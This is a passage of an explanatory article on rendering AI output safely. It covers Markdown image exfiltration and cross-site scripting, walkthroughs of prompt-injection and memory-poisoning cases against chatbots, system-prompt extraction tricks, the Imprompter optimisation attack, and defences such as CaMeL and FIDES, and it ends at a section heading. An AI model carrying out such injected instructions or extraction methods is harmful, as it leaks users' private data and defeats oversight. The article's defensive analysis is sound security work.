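# Displaying AI output safely: cross-site scripting and data theft through rendered answers

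## How a model's answer becomes a web page, and where the danger enters

Large language models (LLMs), the systems behind chatbots such as ChatGPT, produce text. The applications built around them render that text, which means turning it into something viewable, such as a formatted web page, an email or a diagram. Rendering matters for security because a browser treats parts of what it displays as instructions to run a program or contact another computer. An attacker who can influence what the model writes may therefore influence what the user's browser does.

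Two kinds of harm can follow. In cross-site scripting (XSS), an attacker's script runs inside a web page with that page's rights. In exfiltration, private data leaves the application for a place the attacker can read. Both are older than language models. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026), in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, examined eight classes of web attack and concluded that the model usually carries the attacker's influence to a component that trusts its text, rather than creating the underlying flaw. To find the flaw, a developer has to trace an answer's path to the screen.

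### From text to page

Most chat applications expect the model to format its answers in Markdown, a light notation in which asterisks mark bold type and square brackets mark a link. An exclamation mark before the brackets makes an image. Suppose that a user asks for a company's logo and the model emits this line:

```
![Company logo](https://example.com/logo.png?note=meeting-at-noon)
```

So far this is a string of characters and can do nothing. The application hands it to a Markdown parser, a piece of code that converts the notation into HTML, the language of web pages:

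```
<img src="https://example.com/logo.png?note=meeting-at-noon" alt="Company logo">
```

The page then inserts this HTML. To show the image, the browser must fetch it, so it sends a request to example.com for logo.png, with "note=meeting-at-noon" attached. It does this without showing a warning or waiting for the user to click. Many chat interfaces display an answer while the model is still producing it, so the browser may send the request before the user has finished reading.

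The part after the question mark can be any text. The server does not need it to find the picture, but the server's owner can record the whole address. If the model replaces "meeting-at-noon" with a summary of the conversation, the owner can read that summary. The user may not notice the picture. Samoilenko's *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* used a single transparent pixel. In one test, the address carried a block of Python code that ChatGPT had just corrected for the user.

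Every component in this sequence works as designed, but the application makes the mistake of letting text of uncertain origin determine which server the browser contacts and what data it sends there.

### Why the browser's main safeguard does not stop this

Browsers keep websites apart through the same-origin rule. *Same-Origin Policy (SOP)*, a course text on web security, defines an origin as the combination of a scheme (such as https), a host (such as example.com) and a port number. Two pages share an origin only if all three are identical, so a page at chat.example.com and a page at example.com have different origins. PortSwigger's *Same-origin policy (SOP)* explains that browsers attach a user's login cookies to the requests they send, so without the rule any malicious site could read a visitor's Gmail.

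But the same-origin policy mainly restricts reading. W3C's *Same Origin Policy* explains that one origin may generally send information to another but may not receive it. A ban on sending would also ban links between sites, which the web depends on. Theft by image requires only sending. The chat page requests the image and the attacker's server logs the request, so the attacker never has to read anything from the chat page.

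XSS gets past the rule in another way. The answer contains script, the application inserts it as live HTML, and the browser runs it as part of the page. The script has the page's origin, so it can read what the page can read and make requests in the user's name. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a demonstration against the chat site of DeepSeek, a Chinese AI company. The prompt contained an encoded script, the model decoded it, and the site displayed the result as HTML. The script could then read the user's login token from the browser's storage. Rehberger (2024), in *Trust No AI*, lists the case as a full account takeover. An image leak exposes less, since it carries only what the model has put into the image's address.

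The encoding in the DeepSeek case shows why inspecting the model's input is not enough. In ordinary web injection the attacker submits the harmful code directly, but *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (2026) points out that in an LLM application the model itself can generate it. A filter on the incoming prompt would have received a run of letters and digits. The dangerous text first appeared in the answer, so that is where a sanitiser, code that removes or neutralises dangerous markup, has to work.

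Some parsers also pass raw HTML inside Markdown through unchanged, while others turn it into visible text. So the same answer can be inert in one application and run as script in another, even when both use the same model.

### Who really wrote the answer

An attacker seldom has access to a victim's chat window, but can exploit these flaws through prompt injection, which is text that makes a model follow the attacker's instructions. The injection is direct when the attacker enters the text into the model's prompt, and indirect when the text is in content that the model reads, such as a web page or an email. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) introduced indirect injection and observed that earlier research had assumed the attacker was the person prompting the model. In an indirect attack, that person is the victim, and the attacker only needs to place text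 where the model is likely to retrieve it.

When an application renders a model's answers, indirect prompt injection is usually more serious than direct injection, because someone who types an injection into a private chat mostly attacks their own browser. A direct injection can also reach a colleague's browser if the application stores the answer as a support ticket, comment or report and later displays it to them.

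Samoilenko's attack doesn't fit either description neatly. A script on the attacker's website added hidden instructions to whatever a visitor copied, and the visitor then pasted both into ChatGPT. The instructions looked like ordinary user input to the application, so an application cannot safely assume that a user wrote, or even read, everything in the user's message.

The programmer Simon Willison named "prompt injection" after SQL injection, an attack in which a database runs a visitor's input as a command. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) distinguishes prompt injection from jailbreaking, in which a user tricks a model into producing something its maker forbids. Willison warns that developers who confuse the two tend to dismiss prompt injection as a problem that embarrasses the model vendor but doesn't concern them.

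Database programmers have a precise way to keep SQL commands and data apart, but Rehberger notes that no equivalent exists for language models. The application joins its own instructions, the user's question and the retrieved documents into one sequence of tokens (the fragments of text that a model processes), and the model cannot reliably use an instruction's source to determine whether to follow it.

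As a working rule, an application should therefore trust a model's output no more than the least trusted text the model has read. If an assistant answers a question from ten internal documents and one email from a stranger, any part of the answer may come from the stranger, and the application can't reliably tell which. The rule applies for as long as the untrusted text stays in the conversation. In a demonstration against Microsoft's Bing Chat, which the security researcher Johann Rehberger described in Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, the model read a hostile page at the start but emitted the image only a couple of turns later, so a check on only the most recent message would have found nothing.

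Vendors train models to resist injection, and some products try to detect it, which makes attacks less likely to succeed. Willison objects that a product that catches 95% of attacks still fails by the standards of web security, because an attacker can keep trying different wordings. OWASP, the Open Worldwide Application Security Project, is a non-profit foundation that publishes widely used lists of security risks. Its 2026 guidance similarly advises developers to assume that attackers will eventually get past the model's instruction boundary, and to limit what the model's output can reach, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*.

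### The reports of spring 2023

Samoilenko found the image leak in ChatGPT at the end of March 2023. Rehberger found it independently a few days later, according to Rehberger's archived post *ChatGPT Plugins*. Samoilenko described the attack as a set of tricks that exploited no vulnerability. The injected instructions sometimes failed because the model's answers varied between attempts. An attacker could easily make ChatGPT attach the user's previous prompt to the address, but making it attach a password was very difficult.

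That last limit did not always apply. Rehberger's Bing Chat demonstration, from the same spring, used a web page with a secret further down, and the secret reached the test server. Rehberger concluded that hostile instructions in a user comment or an advertisement would have been enough to steal other data on the page.

Microsoft responded faster than OpenAI. Rehberger told Microsoft on April 8, 2023, and Microsoft reported a fix on June 15. The earlier attacks then failed in Rehberger's tests, apparently in part because of a new Content Security Policy, a rule sent with a page that limits where the browser may load content from. OpenAI heard about the ChatGPT flaw on April 9 and at first decided not to fix it, as Rehberger recounted in Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration Vulnerabilities in LLM apps (Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude)*. It began to mitigate the problem only in December 2023, according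 to an update to Willison's (2023) note on Samoilenko's report. That fix was incomplete, and *Trust No AI* records that ChatGPT's mobile apps remained vulnerable.

By the end of 2024 Rehberger had reported the same flaw in at least eleven products, including Anthropic's Claude, Google Bard and GitHub Copilot Chat. In 2026, in Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON*, Rehberger still counted it among the most common security flaws in AI applications. The problem was also still being reported in ChatGPT, where it started. In May 2026 The Hacker News (2026) described a finding by the firm Permiso Security that when ChatGPT summarised a web page, its display automatically fetched Markdown images whose addresses came from that page and made the page's links clickable. Permiso's main concern was phishing, since a link inside ChatGPT's interface looks more trustworthy than the same link on an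 unfamiliar site.

### Three conditions for theft

Willison reduced this run of cases to a test that a developer can apply to a design before anyone has attacked it. Data theft becomes possible when an application combines three things, which Willison named the "lethal trifecta":

- access to private data
- exposure to untrusted content, meaning any text or image an attacker could control
- a way to communicate outward that could carry the data to the attacker

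An email assistant can meet all three conditions with ordinary features. The mailbox is private, anyone who knows the address can write to it, and the assistant's answers may contain images, which are a means of communication even though a developer might not think of them that way. In a note on GitHub Copilot Chat, Willison (2024) says that if a chat interface handles both private and untrusted data, support for Markdown images is enough to meet the third condition. GitHub responded by no longer displaying images from untrusted domains.

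Removing any one condition prevents this kind of theft. But people want an assistant because it can see their private data, and hostile text can reach it in too many ways. Willison therefore considers the outward channel generally the easiest to remove. Rehberger goes further and calls it the only part of the system where enforcement is realistic. Their reasoning is sound, because a browser or server can refuse a request by a fixed rule even if hostile text has manipulated the model. Removing the channel is still a large job, since Willison also describes the ways a tool might send data out as almost limitless, and they include links that send data only when the user clicks them.

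The test covers only data theft through the model, so an application can pass it and still be unsafe. A chatbot with no access to private data can still display a phishing link. It can also be vulnerable to XSS, because a script running in the page can read private data from the page or the user's account and make its own requests, even if the model has no access to that data.

### What OWASP calls the flaw

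Number five on OWASP's 2025 list of the ten main risks for LLM applications covers this subject. *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* defines the risk as "insufficient validation, sanitization, and handling of the outputs generated by large language models" before they go to other components. This definition also covers applications that run the model's text as a system command or a database query. For display, the entry's recommendations include encoding the output, so that the browser shows markup as text, and setting a strict Content Security Policy.

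OWASP separates improper output handling from overreliance, which means depending too much on the accuracy of a model's answers. If an AI medical assistant states the wrong dose on a safe page and a nurse acts on it, that is overreliance, and fact-checking would help. Fact-checking would not stop the page from running a script included in the answer, which is improper output handling even if the dose is right.

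One of the entry's examples fits poorly with its own definition. A web application displays a model's answer without sanitising it, a script runs in the victim's browser, and OWASP attributes this to insufficient validation of prompts. Better checks on prompts might have stopped that attack, but the application would still have run the next script to appear in an answer. OWASP's advice to treat the model "as any other user" also needs careful interpretation. The relevant user is the outsider whose email the model has just read, not the employee who is logged in.

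OWASP published a newer edition of its list, for 2026, in August. According to Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), an analysis by a security vendor, improper output handling fell from fifth place to tenth, further than any other entry. For the first time, OWASP checked its community vote against 7,714 recorded incidents, 6,639 of which had enough detail to classify. The vote still counted for three-quarters of the ranking. The fall is weak evidence that applications now display output more safely, because a rank only compares one risk with the others. Advait Patel, a developer of security software quoted by ReversingLabs, likewise said that the risks above it had become more urgent.

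The entry now ranks lower but covers more, explicitly including terminals that act on control codes in a model's text and displays that automatically fetch external resources named in an answer. The 2025 edition already had a scenario in which a website summariser sends private data to an attacker's server, but it did not specifically name automatic fetching as the route. Under the 2026 wording, an application that strips every script from an answer but still loads images from any address has an output-handling flaw.

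## Mapping the attack paths and choosing where to cut them

Willison's test passes or fails an application as a whole. To decide what to change, a developer whose design fails needs to know which hostile text could reach which data and how that data could leave. The developer can map these attack paths by combining one item from each of three lists: the sources of untrusted text, the private data the model can access, and the outlets, meaning every feature through which data can leave the application.

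### Drawing up the inventory

Suppose that a software company gives its support staff an assistant that reads customers' tickets, looks things up and drafts replies. Its lists might look like this:

| Untrusted sources | Private data within reach | Outlets |
|---|---|---|
| Customers' tickets | Customer account records | Images in the answer |
| Posts on the public help forum | Other customers' tickets | Links in the answer |
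| Web pages the assistant fetches | Internal engineering notes | Link previews in the staff chat |
| | The staff member's mailbox | The web-fetch tool |
| | | Email replies to customers |

Any source can combine with any data store and any outlet, so there are 3 × 4 × 5 = 60 paths. In one path, a forum post makes the model put an account record into the address of an image. The reviewer writes down what blocks each path or marks it as open.

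Closing one outlet removes 3 × 4 = 12 paths, disconnecting one data store removes 15, and dropping one source removes 20. The web-fetch tool is both a source and an outlet, because it brings in pages and sends out addresses. Removing it leaves 2 × 4 × 4 = 32 paths.

The counts help a team compare changes, but they don't measure risk, because an attacker needs only one open path. If the company drops the forum, a third of the paths disappear, but someone who can file a ticket still has all of theirs. The total reaches zero only when one of the lists is empty.

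Untrusted sources are easy to leave off a list. Whether a source is untrusted depends on who can write the text, not where the application keeps it. Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* describes an attack by the security firm Zenity Labs that began with an email to a support desk. Software turned the email into a ticket in the company's internal tracker, where a developer's coding assistant read it and followed the instructions inside. Outlets can also be easy to miss because they seem harmless. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could email the user's own inbox without asking, and the mail display loaded external images, so data could leave when the user opened the message.

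### Prompts that arrive in a link

Many AI sites accept a prompt in the web address, so anyone can write a link that opens the assistant with a prompt they chose. *Reprompt* (January 2026), from the data-security company Varonis, describes how this worked against the consumer version of Microsoft Copilot. The victim clicked a genuine Microsoft link, and Copilot ran the attacker's prompt in the victim's logged-in session as though the victim had typed it.

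Copilot had a safeguard against putting private data into the addresses it fetched, but it covered only the first request. The researchers told the model to do everything twice. In one test, the safeguard stripped a secret phrase from the first request but not the second. The attacker's server then replied with further instructions to send the user's location, personal details and a summary of the last conversation, one after another, so inspecting the original link alone would not have revealed what the attack was taking. The theft continued even if the victim closed the tab. Microsoft had patched the flaw by the time Varonis published. The flaw did not affect the enterprise product, Microsoft 365 Copilot, but Varonis later found a similar attack chain there, called SearchLeak.

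A second attack on consumer Copilot, which Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) disclosed in August, submitted a prompt without the user's consent. A question in a link normally only filled the input box, and the user had to press Enter to submit it, but an undocumented setting in the address submitted it when the page loaded. The researchers learned of the setting by repeatedly asking Copilot why automatic submission was impossible. The prompt could then make Copilot search the victim's connected Gmail, Google Drive and calendar, and send out what it found by asking it to summarise a web address that contained the data. Varonis reported the flaw in December 2025, and Microsoft patched it on August 18, 2026. Microsoft rated its severity at 8.8 out of 10, according to TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions*. Varonis found no sign that anyone had exploited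 it.

An application that accepts prompts from links should list the URL as an untrusted source. It can fill the input box and wait for the user to press Enter, but doing so doesn't prove that the user read a long prompt. Varonis advises vendors to treat such text as untrusted at every later step, including repeated and follow-up requests.

### Memory that outlives the attack

Some assistants save facts about the user and add them to later conversations. If an injection can write to that memory, it can affect those conversations even when they don't include the document that delivered it.

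Embrace The Red describes how Rehberger demonstrated this against Microsoft 365 Copilot, using a biography of Albert Einstein with instructions buried in the middle. The user asked for a summary and got a normal one, which ended by asking whether the information was helpful. Answering either "yes" or "no" caused the model to save a memory. In later conversations, whenever the user pasted in a password, Copilot put it in an address on Rehberger's server and the display fetched that address. Injected text could also delete memories.

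Microsoft reported the memory flaws fixed in December 2025 and closed the outlet on March 5, 2026. Rehberger suspects that the memory fix consists of more model training and input blocking, in which case a newly worded attack might get around it. According to Microsoft's documentation in April 2026, memory changes produce no audit log entries, so an administrator would have little evidence of how a memory got there. Rehberger recommends that an assistant save a memory automatically only if the user's own message clearly asked for it, and otherwise only suggest saving it.

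Other products had the same weakness. In CoSnitch, a web page that Copilot summarised could write to memory. Varonis notes that the entry would survive a password change and re-enrolment of the device. The Hacker News describes ZombieAgent, an attack that persisted through ChatGPT's memory.

Memory is both a source and a data store in the inventory, so if the support company adds memory, the number of paths rises from 60 to 4 × 5 × 5 = 100.

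### What each cut costs the user

Keeping untrusted text out cuts the attack path most thoroughly, but it is usually the least practical option. A support assistant, for example, can't do its job without reading tickets. Willison reports that Cursor, whose coding assistant Zenity attacked, advised users to connect it only to sources with trusted content. That advice would have ruled out the company's own ticket tracker.

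Keeping private data out is less convenient, because staff have to look things up themselves. The company can reduce this inconvenience by splitting the work between two modes. One could read the web and the forum but have no access to private data, and the other could read tickets and all four data stores but have no web access. If the two share no conversation or memory, the web mode has no attack paths and the ticket mode has 1 × 4 × 4 = 16. Staff can no longer ask one question that needs both modes.

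Closing outlets tends to inconvenience users least. Few people would miss external images in a support answer or previews in the staff chat. Showing links as plain text is a little more annoying, since the user has to copy them. With those three outlets closed, the ticket mode has four paths left, all ending in an email to a customer. The company can't close that outlet, because the assistant's purpose is to reply. Restricting replies to the person who filed the ticket doesn't help, because that person may be the attacker.

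A common compromise is to have the agent (a model that acts by calling tools, such as a function that sends email) ask the user before each risky action. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* argues that this scales poorly, makes people less vigilant and takes away the autonomy that made the agent useful. Attackers can also exploit the confirmation step itself. The Hacker News describes an attack named Lies-in-the-Loop, which used people's trust in confirmation dialogs in Claude Code and Copilot Chat to run malicious code.

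### The dispute over model resistance

Another approach is to leave every path in place and try to make the model ignore hostile instructions. This appeals to vendors because users lose no features.

Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) gives the case for it. Google trained its Gemini 2.5 models on examples of attacks. Classifiers, separate models trained to recognise malicious instructions, scan emails and files and remove what they flag before Gemini answers. Google also places reminders around the content telling the model to stick to the user's task, removes suspicious links, asks for confirmation of some actions and notifies users when it has stopped an attack. Google argues that together these layers make attacks harder and more expensive, and push attackers towards methods that are easier to detect. Resistance can also help against attacks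 that closing an outlet wouldn't stop, such as hostile text that tries to make an assistant delete a calendar event.

Willison takes the objection to 95% detection further, arguing that in application security even "99% is a failing grade". If each attempt has a 1% chance of success and the attempts are independent, 100 attempts give a 63% chance of at least one success. Real attempts aren't independent, and an attacker who learns from failures may do better. *The Economist* had compared AI developers with Victorian engineers, who overbuilt bridges because they couldn't trust their iron. Willison agrees that language models are unpredictable but rejects overbuilding as a defense against a deliberate attacker.

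Rehberger also prefers to enforce security at the outward channel. Writing on Embrace The Red, he worries that as models become more robust, people start to assume the model will enforce security boundaries and become less careful themselves.

Resistance also inconveniences users, because the model refuses some harmless requests. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) found in *Can CaMeLs Talk?* that Claude Fable 5 refused 52 of 97 harmless tasks in a test environment derived from a prompt-injection benchmark. They suspect that the model associated the environment with attacks, so the refusal rate in ordinary use is probably much lower.

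Training and classifiers are worth having, but a reviewer should not mark an attack path as blocked because of them. Gemini's display never loads external images, and Google cites this fixed rule, not the model's training, as the reason that EchoLeak, a leak through images in Microsoft 365 Copilot, does not apply to Gemini. Fixed rules can also have gaps. Anthropic once let Claude's web-fetch tool follow links found inside pages it had fetched, and a researcher used a chain of such links to spell out a user's name. Anthropic removed that permission, which stopped the technique however an attacker worded the prompt, an assurance that training cannot give.

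### Tracking untrusted data

The support company's last four paths need a different kind of cut, which lets the assistant read a hostile ticket but limits what the ticket can influence. Willison (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, recommends a paper by eleven researchers, who acknowledge that their designs gain security by deliberately making agents unable to solve arbitrary tasks.

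CaMeL, from Google DeepMind, is the best-known design of this kind. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, welcomed it after two and a half years of "alarmingly little progress". CaMeL builds on his earlier idea of using two models. Suppose a staff member asks for a summary of a ticket to be sent to the billing team. A privileged model, which sees only this request, writes a short program that fetches the ticket, has it summarised and sends the summary to billing. A quarantined model with no tools reads the ticket and writes the summary. If the ticket contains an instruction to email someone else, the system doesn't send that email, because the program has no such step and the privileged model never reads the ticket.

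The ticket can still affect what the summary contains. CaMeL therefore records where each value came from and who may read it (*CaMeLoT*, 2026). Before each tool call, it checks these records against a policy and allows or denies the call.

Peters-Gill and colleagues measured CaMeL in systems where one agent delegates work to others. They tested five models on 949 attacked tasks each, with the data policies switched off to isolate the effect of separating plan from data. Attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL and 0.2% with it. One model, GPT-5.5, resisted every attack without CaMeL, which may be due more to weak attacks in the benchmark than to the model's robustness. On a separate set of 112 professional tasks, CaMeL lowered the completion rate by 21.6 percentage points on average, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest models.

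In every attack that still succeeded, an agent that had correctly treated some text as untrusted data pasted it into its instructions to another agent, which treated the whole message as a trusted request. In one demonstration, text in a database of job applicants made a notification agent send the applicants' details to an outside address, although every agent in the system ran CaMeL. The team's extended version, which passes data between agents separately from instructions, stopped all the attacks but lowered task completion by another 3.2 points.

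A fixed plan also works poorly for some tasks. An agent that operates a computer by looking at the screen can't know in advance what it will see, so its plan needs many branches. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) found that agents using such plans kept at most 57% of the performance of leading models. Hostile content couldn't add steps to the plan, but it could influence which branch the agent took. For example, an advertisement made to look like a cookie notice could get the agent to click through to the attacker's site.

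Microsoft's FIDES lets an agent choose each step as it goes, and labels all the data the agent reads. One label records whether the data is trusted, and another records who may see it. A result made from several pieces of data gets the most restrictive combination of their labels. Before each tool call, FIDES checks the labels against a fixed policy on what the tool accepts. It can also store untrusted text in a variable hidden from the main model, and have a quarantined model answer a narrow question about the text, such as whether an email contains a meeting request. A yes-or-no answer leaves an attacker little room to pass instructions to the main model.

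Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, tested FIDES with GPT-4o on AgentDojo, a benchmark of everyday office tasks with planted injections. An ordinary agent fell for 152 injections. With policy checks on, the researchers counted none, after setting aside a few that the benchmark had scored as successes. Some of those had only altered text, so an injection can still distort a summary that the user reads. Without attacks, the agents completed these percentages of their tasks:

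| | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| Ordinary agent, policy checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| FIDES, policy checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

The paper emphasises that FIDES beats an ordinary agent under the same checks by about 8 points on average. But it scores about 34 points lower than an agent with no checks, which is what most developers would be replacing. Part of that loss is unavoidable, because many banking tasks told the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which the policy exists to prevent. Using a better model, OpenAI's o1, recovered some of the rest, raising completion of the travel tasks from 41% to 68%.

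Later work suggests that the choice of policy matters as much as the mechanism. In *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026), an agent completed 33.2% of harmless AgentDojo tasks under the FIDES policy and 62.5% under a policy based on where data came from. It completed 83.7% with AgentDojo's own defence, in which a model picks the tools a task needs and blocks the rest, but that defence let 20 injections through in tests by Costa and colleagues.

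The main practical complaint is that labels only get stricter, so after an agent reads one hostile web page, everything it does for the rest of the session counts as untrusted. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) lets the agent open a temporary branch to read such a page. The branch can return only data in a fixed format, such as a number or an item from a set list, and the agent discards the rest. Across two benchmarks, the agents completed 64.2% to 91% of tasks, and none of the attacks in 1,320 protected runs succeeded. Two FIDES setups let some attacks through in the same tests, but Kravchenko's team had configured those setups and acknowledges that the policies didn't cover all the rules one benchmark tested.

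Developers can already try labelling with FIDES, an experimental feature of Microsoft's Agent Framework that the company announced in May in *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026). Its default is risky because a tool that the developer forgets to label counts as trusted and public. Labels also need to follow data into storage, since untrusted text can influence an agent through its memory in a later session, as Cai and Wen (2026) point out in *Ghost in the Agent*. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026), a survey, finds that existing tracking methods add enough running time to limit their use where users expect quick answers.

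For the support assistant, labels determine what an email may contain. Staff and customer A may read A's ticket, and staff and customer B may read B's. Only people on both lists may read a draft based on both tickets, {staff, A} ∩ {staff, B} = {staff}, so the policy stops it from going to B, whatever instructions B's ticket contains. A draft based only on B's ticket and B's account record can go out. The drawback is that once the assistant has opened A's ticket for comparison, a later reply to B in that session needs approval even if it uses nothing from A.

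The same check has to cover what the application displays. A policy that examines only tool calls would block the email but still let the answer on the staff member's screen load an image whose URL contains A's data. Microsoft suggests treating a rendered link to any host outside an allow-list as a public channel, so private data can't go into it.

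## What an attacker can extract through the model: session data and training data

Two kinds of attacker might want customer A's data from the support assistant. The first is the user, who could be a curious employee, or another customer if the company puts the assistant on its public website. This attacker doesn't need a rendering flaw because they can read the data in the answer. The second uses indirect injection to attack someone else's session and can't see the answers, so they need an outlet that sends them the data.

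An application that handles private data usually needs both image blocking and permission checks. Blocking images doesn't stop the user from reading an answer. Permission checks stop the user from reading other people's records, but they do much less against an absent attacker, whose injected instructions run with the victim's permissions.

An attacker can extract two kinds of data through the model. Session data is whatever the model can see or fetch during a session, such as its instructions, the conversation, memories, documents and tool results. Training data is the text that the model's developer used to set its weights, the numbers that determine its output. Session data differs between sessions, but every user of a model queries the same weights.

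### System prompts and tool lists

Most applications start each conversation with a system prompt that sets out the model's role, its rules and the tools it can call. Some developers assume this text is private and put sensitive information in it. Rehberger points out that the system prompt and the user's message share a trust boundary, so a user can often retrieve the system prompt easily. The security company Lakera made a game based on this problem, called Gandalf, in which players try to get a model to reveal a secret.

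Developers often respond by adding a line that tells the model not to reveal its instructions. This only makes answers that reveal them less likely, and the secret is still part of the input the model uses to compute every answer. An access check, by contrast, runs outside the model, looks up who is asking and withholds the data if that person has no right to it.

Microsoft's attempts to protect Copilot's system prompt show that blocking one extraction method tends to leave others open. Embrace The Red recounts that Rehberger once got around the protection by asking for the prompt in German. Microsoft later blocked that method, and Copilot also refused to list its tools, but it revealed their names when Rehberger asked it to put them into a structured document.

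A filter that searches answers for the secret won't match a translation or paraphrase of it. Yes-or-no answers can also reveal a secret without containing any part of it. A four-digit code has 10,000 possible values, and each truthful answer can rule out half of those that remain, so fourteen answers are enough to find the code (2^14 = 16,384).

Even a tool list can show an attacker where to look next. Copilot's list included a tool for creating documents, which made Rehberger wonder whether Copilot could render HTML. Rehberger investigated, found the HTML preview, and later used it to steal data.

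Attackers can also automate the questioning. *Just Ask* (2026) began with requests to Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, for its own system prompt and those of its subagents. The paper then presents an agent that recovers other models' prompts through conversation alone and checks whether its results are consistent. The recovered text can differ in wording from the original and still describe the same rules.

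*Extracting System Prompt of LLM Services in Complex (Agentic) Settings* (2026) reports that extraction works less well on long, structured prompts with added defences, and on services that show users only part of the model's output. These measures may be enough for a company that wants to make its prompt harder to copy, but they are not enough to protect a password in the prompt. The safe approach is to write the system prompt as though users will read it. Passwords and access keys belong in the code that carries out a tool call, where the model never sees them.

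### Documents, memories and other customers' records

A model can quote only the tickets that the application gives it, so leaks of other people's records often start in the retrieval code. Suppose the company opens its assistant to customers, and the assistant searches the whole ticket database through one shared account. Customer B describes a fault, the search returns customer A's ticket because A had the same fault, and the model quotes it, so B learns A's details without attacking anything.

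The retrieval code should therefore check permissions before any text reaches the model:

```
find_tickets(
    customer_id = login_session.customer_id,
    search_text = model_request.search_text
)
```

Here the application takes the customer's identity from the login session and only the search terms from the model. If it took the identity from the model too, B could read A's tickets by getting the model to write A's number. Saved memories, earlier conversations and cached answers need the same check, because the application can mix up users in any of them.

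This permission check would not have stopped Rehberger's demonstration in Microsoft Word, because the victim was entitled to read the email that was stolen. The victim opened a document someone had shared with them and typed only a greeting to Copilot. Instructions in the document made Copilot search the victim's mailbox for a particular email and send its contents to Rehberger's server in the URL of a font.

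A second demonstration extracted memories from the consumer version of Copilot in Microsoft's Edge browser. It used the same kind of follow-up question as the Einstein biography attack. When the victim replied "yes", Copilot opened a web address that contained what it had remembered about them. When Rehberger retested the attack in 2026, Copilot blocked the file, probably because Microsoft had added guardrails and input filtering.

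Permission checks still limit what an attacker can take through another user's session. An injection that reaches a junior employee's session can collect only what that employee can open, unless the assistant has wider access than the employee.

### Imprompter

Rehberger wrote these instructions by hand, and anyone who found them could read them. In *Imprompter*, Fu, Li and colleagues (2024) used an optimisation program to produce instructions that a person could not understand but a model would follow.

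In one scenario, a job applicant finds a prompt on a sharing site that promises to improve cover letters. The prompt looks like a jumble of symbols and words from several languages. The applicant pastes it into a chat that contains the letter and gets a reply that looks empty. The reply contains an invisible image whose address carries the applicant's name and contact details to the attacker.

The method requires the weights of an open model similar to the one in the target product. Call the conversation *c*, the attacker's prompt *x* and the output the attacker wants *y*. Here *y* is an image whose address contains details from *c*. The program looks for the *x* that gives the lowest average value, over many sample conversations, of

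L(x) = −log P(y | c, x)

A lower value means the model is more likely to write *y*. One wrong character can stop the image from loading, so the researchers gave extra weight to the fixed part of *y* that comes before the stolen details.

The search started from a readable instruction. For each position in the prompt, the program shortlisted 256 replacement tokens using the model's gradients, which estimate how a change would affect the loss. It tested a random sample of these replacements from all positions, kept the single best one and repeated the process. Barring English words from the replacements usually made the result unreadable. Most runs took less than a day, and those on the two smaller text models needed only one graphics card.

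The researchers then tried the prompts on two commercial chatbots, ChatGLM and Mistral's LeChat. In 98 general conversations, LeChat produced a correctly formed image address 84.7% of the time and ChatGLM 99.0%. About 70% of the words in LeChat's addresses and about 63% of those in ChatGLM's came from the conversation.

A separate test used 25 conversations about job, visa and other applications. LeChat produced a correct web address more than 90% of the time, and about 80% of the terms it sent were real personal details. The "nearly 80% success rate" in the paper's summary refers to this precision, not to the share of people whose data leaked. The attack recovered only about half of the personal details in each conversation. Each product was tested once per conversation, and one prompt that had worked on ChatGLM's open model extracted nothing useful from the ChatGLM product.

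Optimisation strengthened the attack more on some models than on others. On Mistral's open model, a plain instruction produced the right format 86% of the time and the best optimised prompt 90%, so optimisation helped mainly by disguising the instruction. On ChatGLM's open model, the plain image instruction never worked, while the best optimised one worked about 90% of the time.

Fu and colleagues considered rejecting prompts that look statistically unnatural, but doubted this would be reliable because attackers can also make disguised prompts that look natural. Willison (2024) reports in *This prompt can make an AI chatbot identify and extract personal details* that Mistral instead restricted Markdown images in LeChat. That restriction would not protect an assistant that can also open web addresses, and Fu and colleagues had optimised prompts for that kind of tool too.

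### What it means for a model to memorise text

Training adjusts a model's weights to make each next token in the training text more probable. The model mostly learns general patterns this way, but its weights can also store particular passages. Cooper (2026), in *Playing Whack-a-Mole with misconceptions about memorization, extraction, and copyright*, distinguishes memorisation, which concerns the weights, from extraction, which concerns the output. A model may have memorised a passage that nobody can extract.

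*Estimating near-verbatim extraction risk in language models with decoding-constrained beam search* (2026) describes the usual test for extraction. Researchers give the model the first 50 tokens of a 100-token passage from known training text and check whether it continues with exactly the other 50 (about 37 words).

The length of a match matters because a fluent model can guess short phrases. Suppose a model has an 80% chance of guessing each next token of an ordinary passage it has never seen. It would match five tokens in a row about a third of the time (0.8^5 ≈ 0.33), but fifty in a row about once in 70,000 attempts (0.8^50 ≈ 0.000014). In *Scalable Extraction of Training Data from (Production) Language Models*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2023) set their threshold by looking for overlaps between large training datasets and news articles written later. Apart from quotations, they found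 none longer than 25 tokens, so they doubled that figure to 50.

Outsiders seldom have a commercial model's training data. To check whether a passage the model produced came from that data, they can search for it on the web, compare it with a large collection of text that the developer probably used, or ask the developer. They can also run the same extraction procedure on a book published after the model's training ended. If the procedure appears to extract that book too, it is producing false positives.

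Duplication raises the risk because each copy of a passage gives training another chance to make that exact sequence more probable.

### From GPT-2 to ChatGPT

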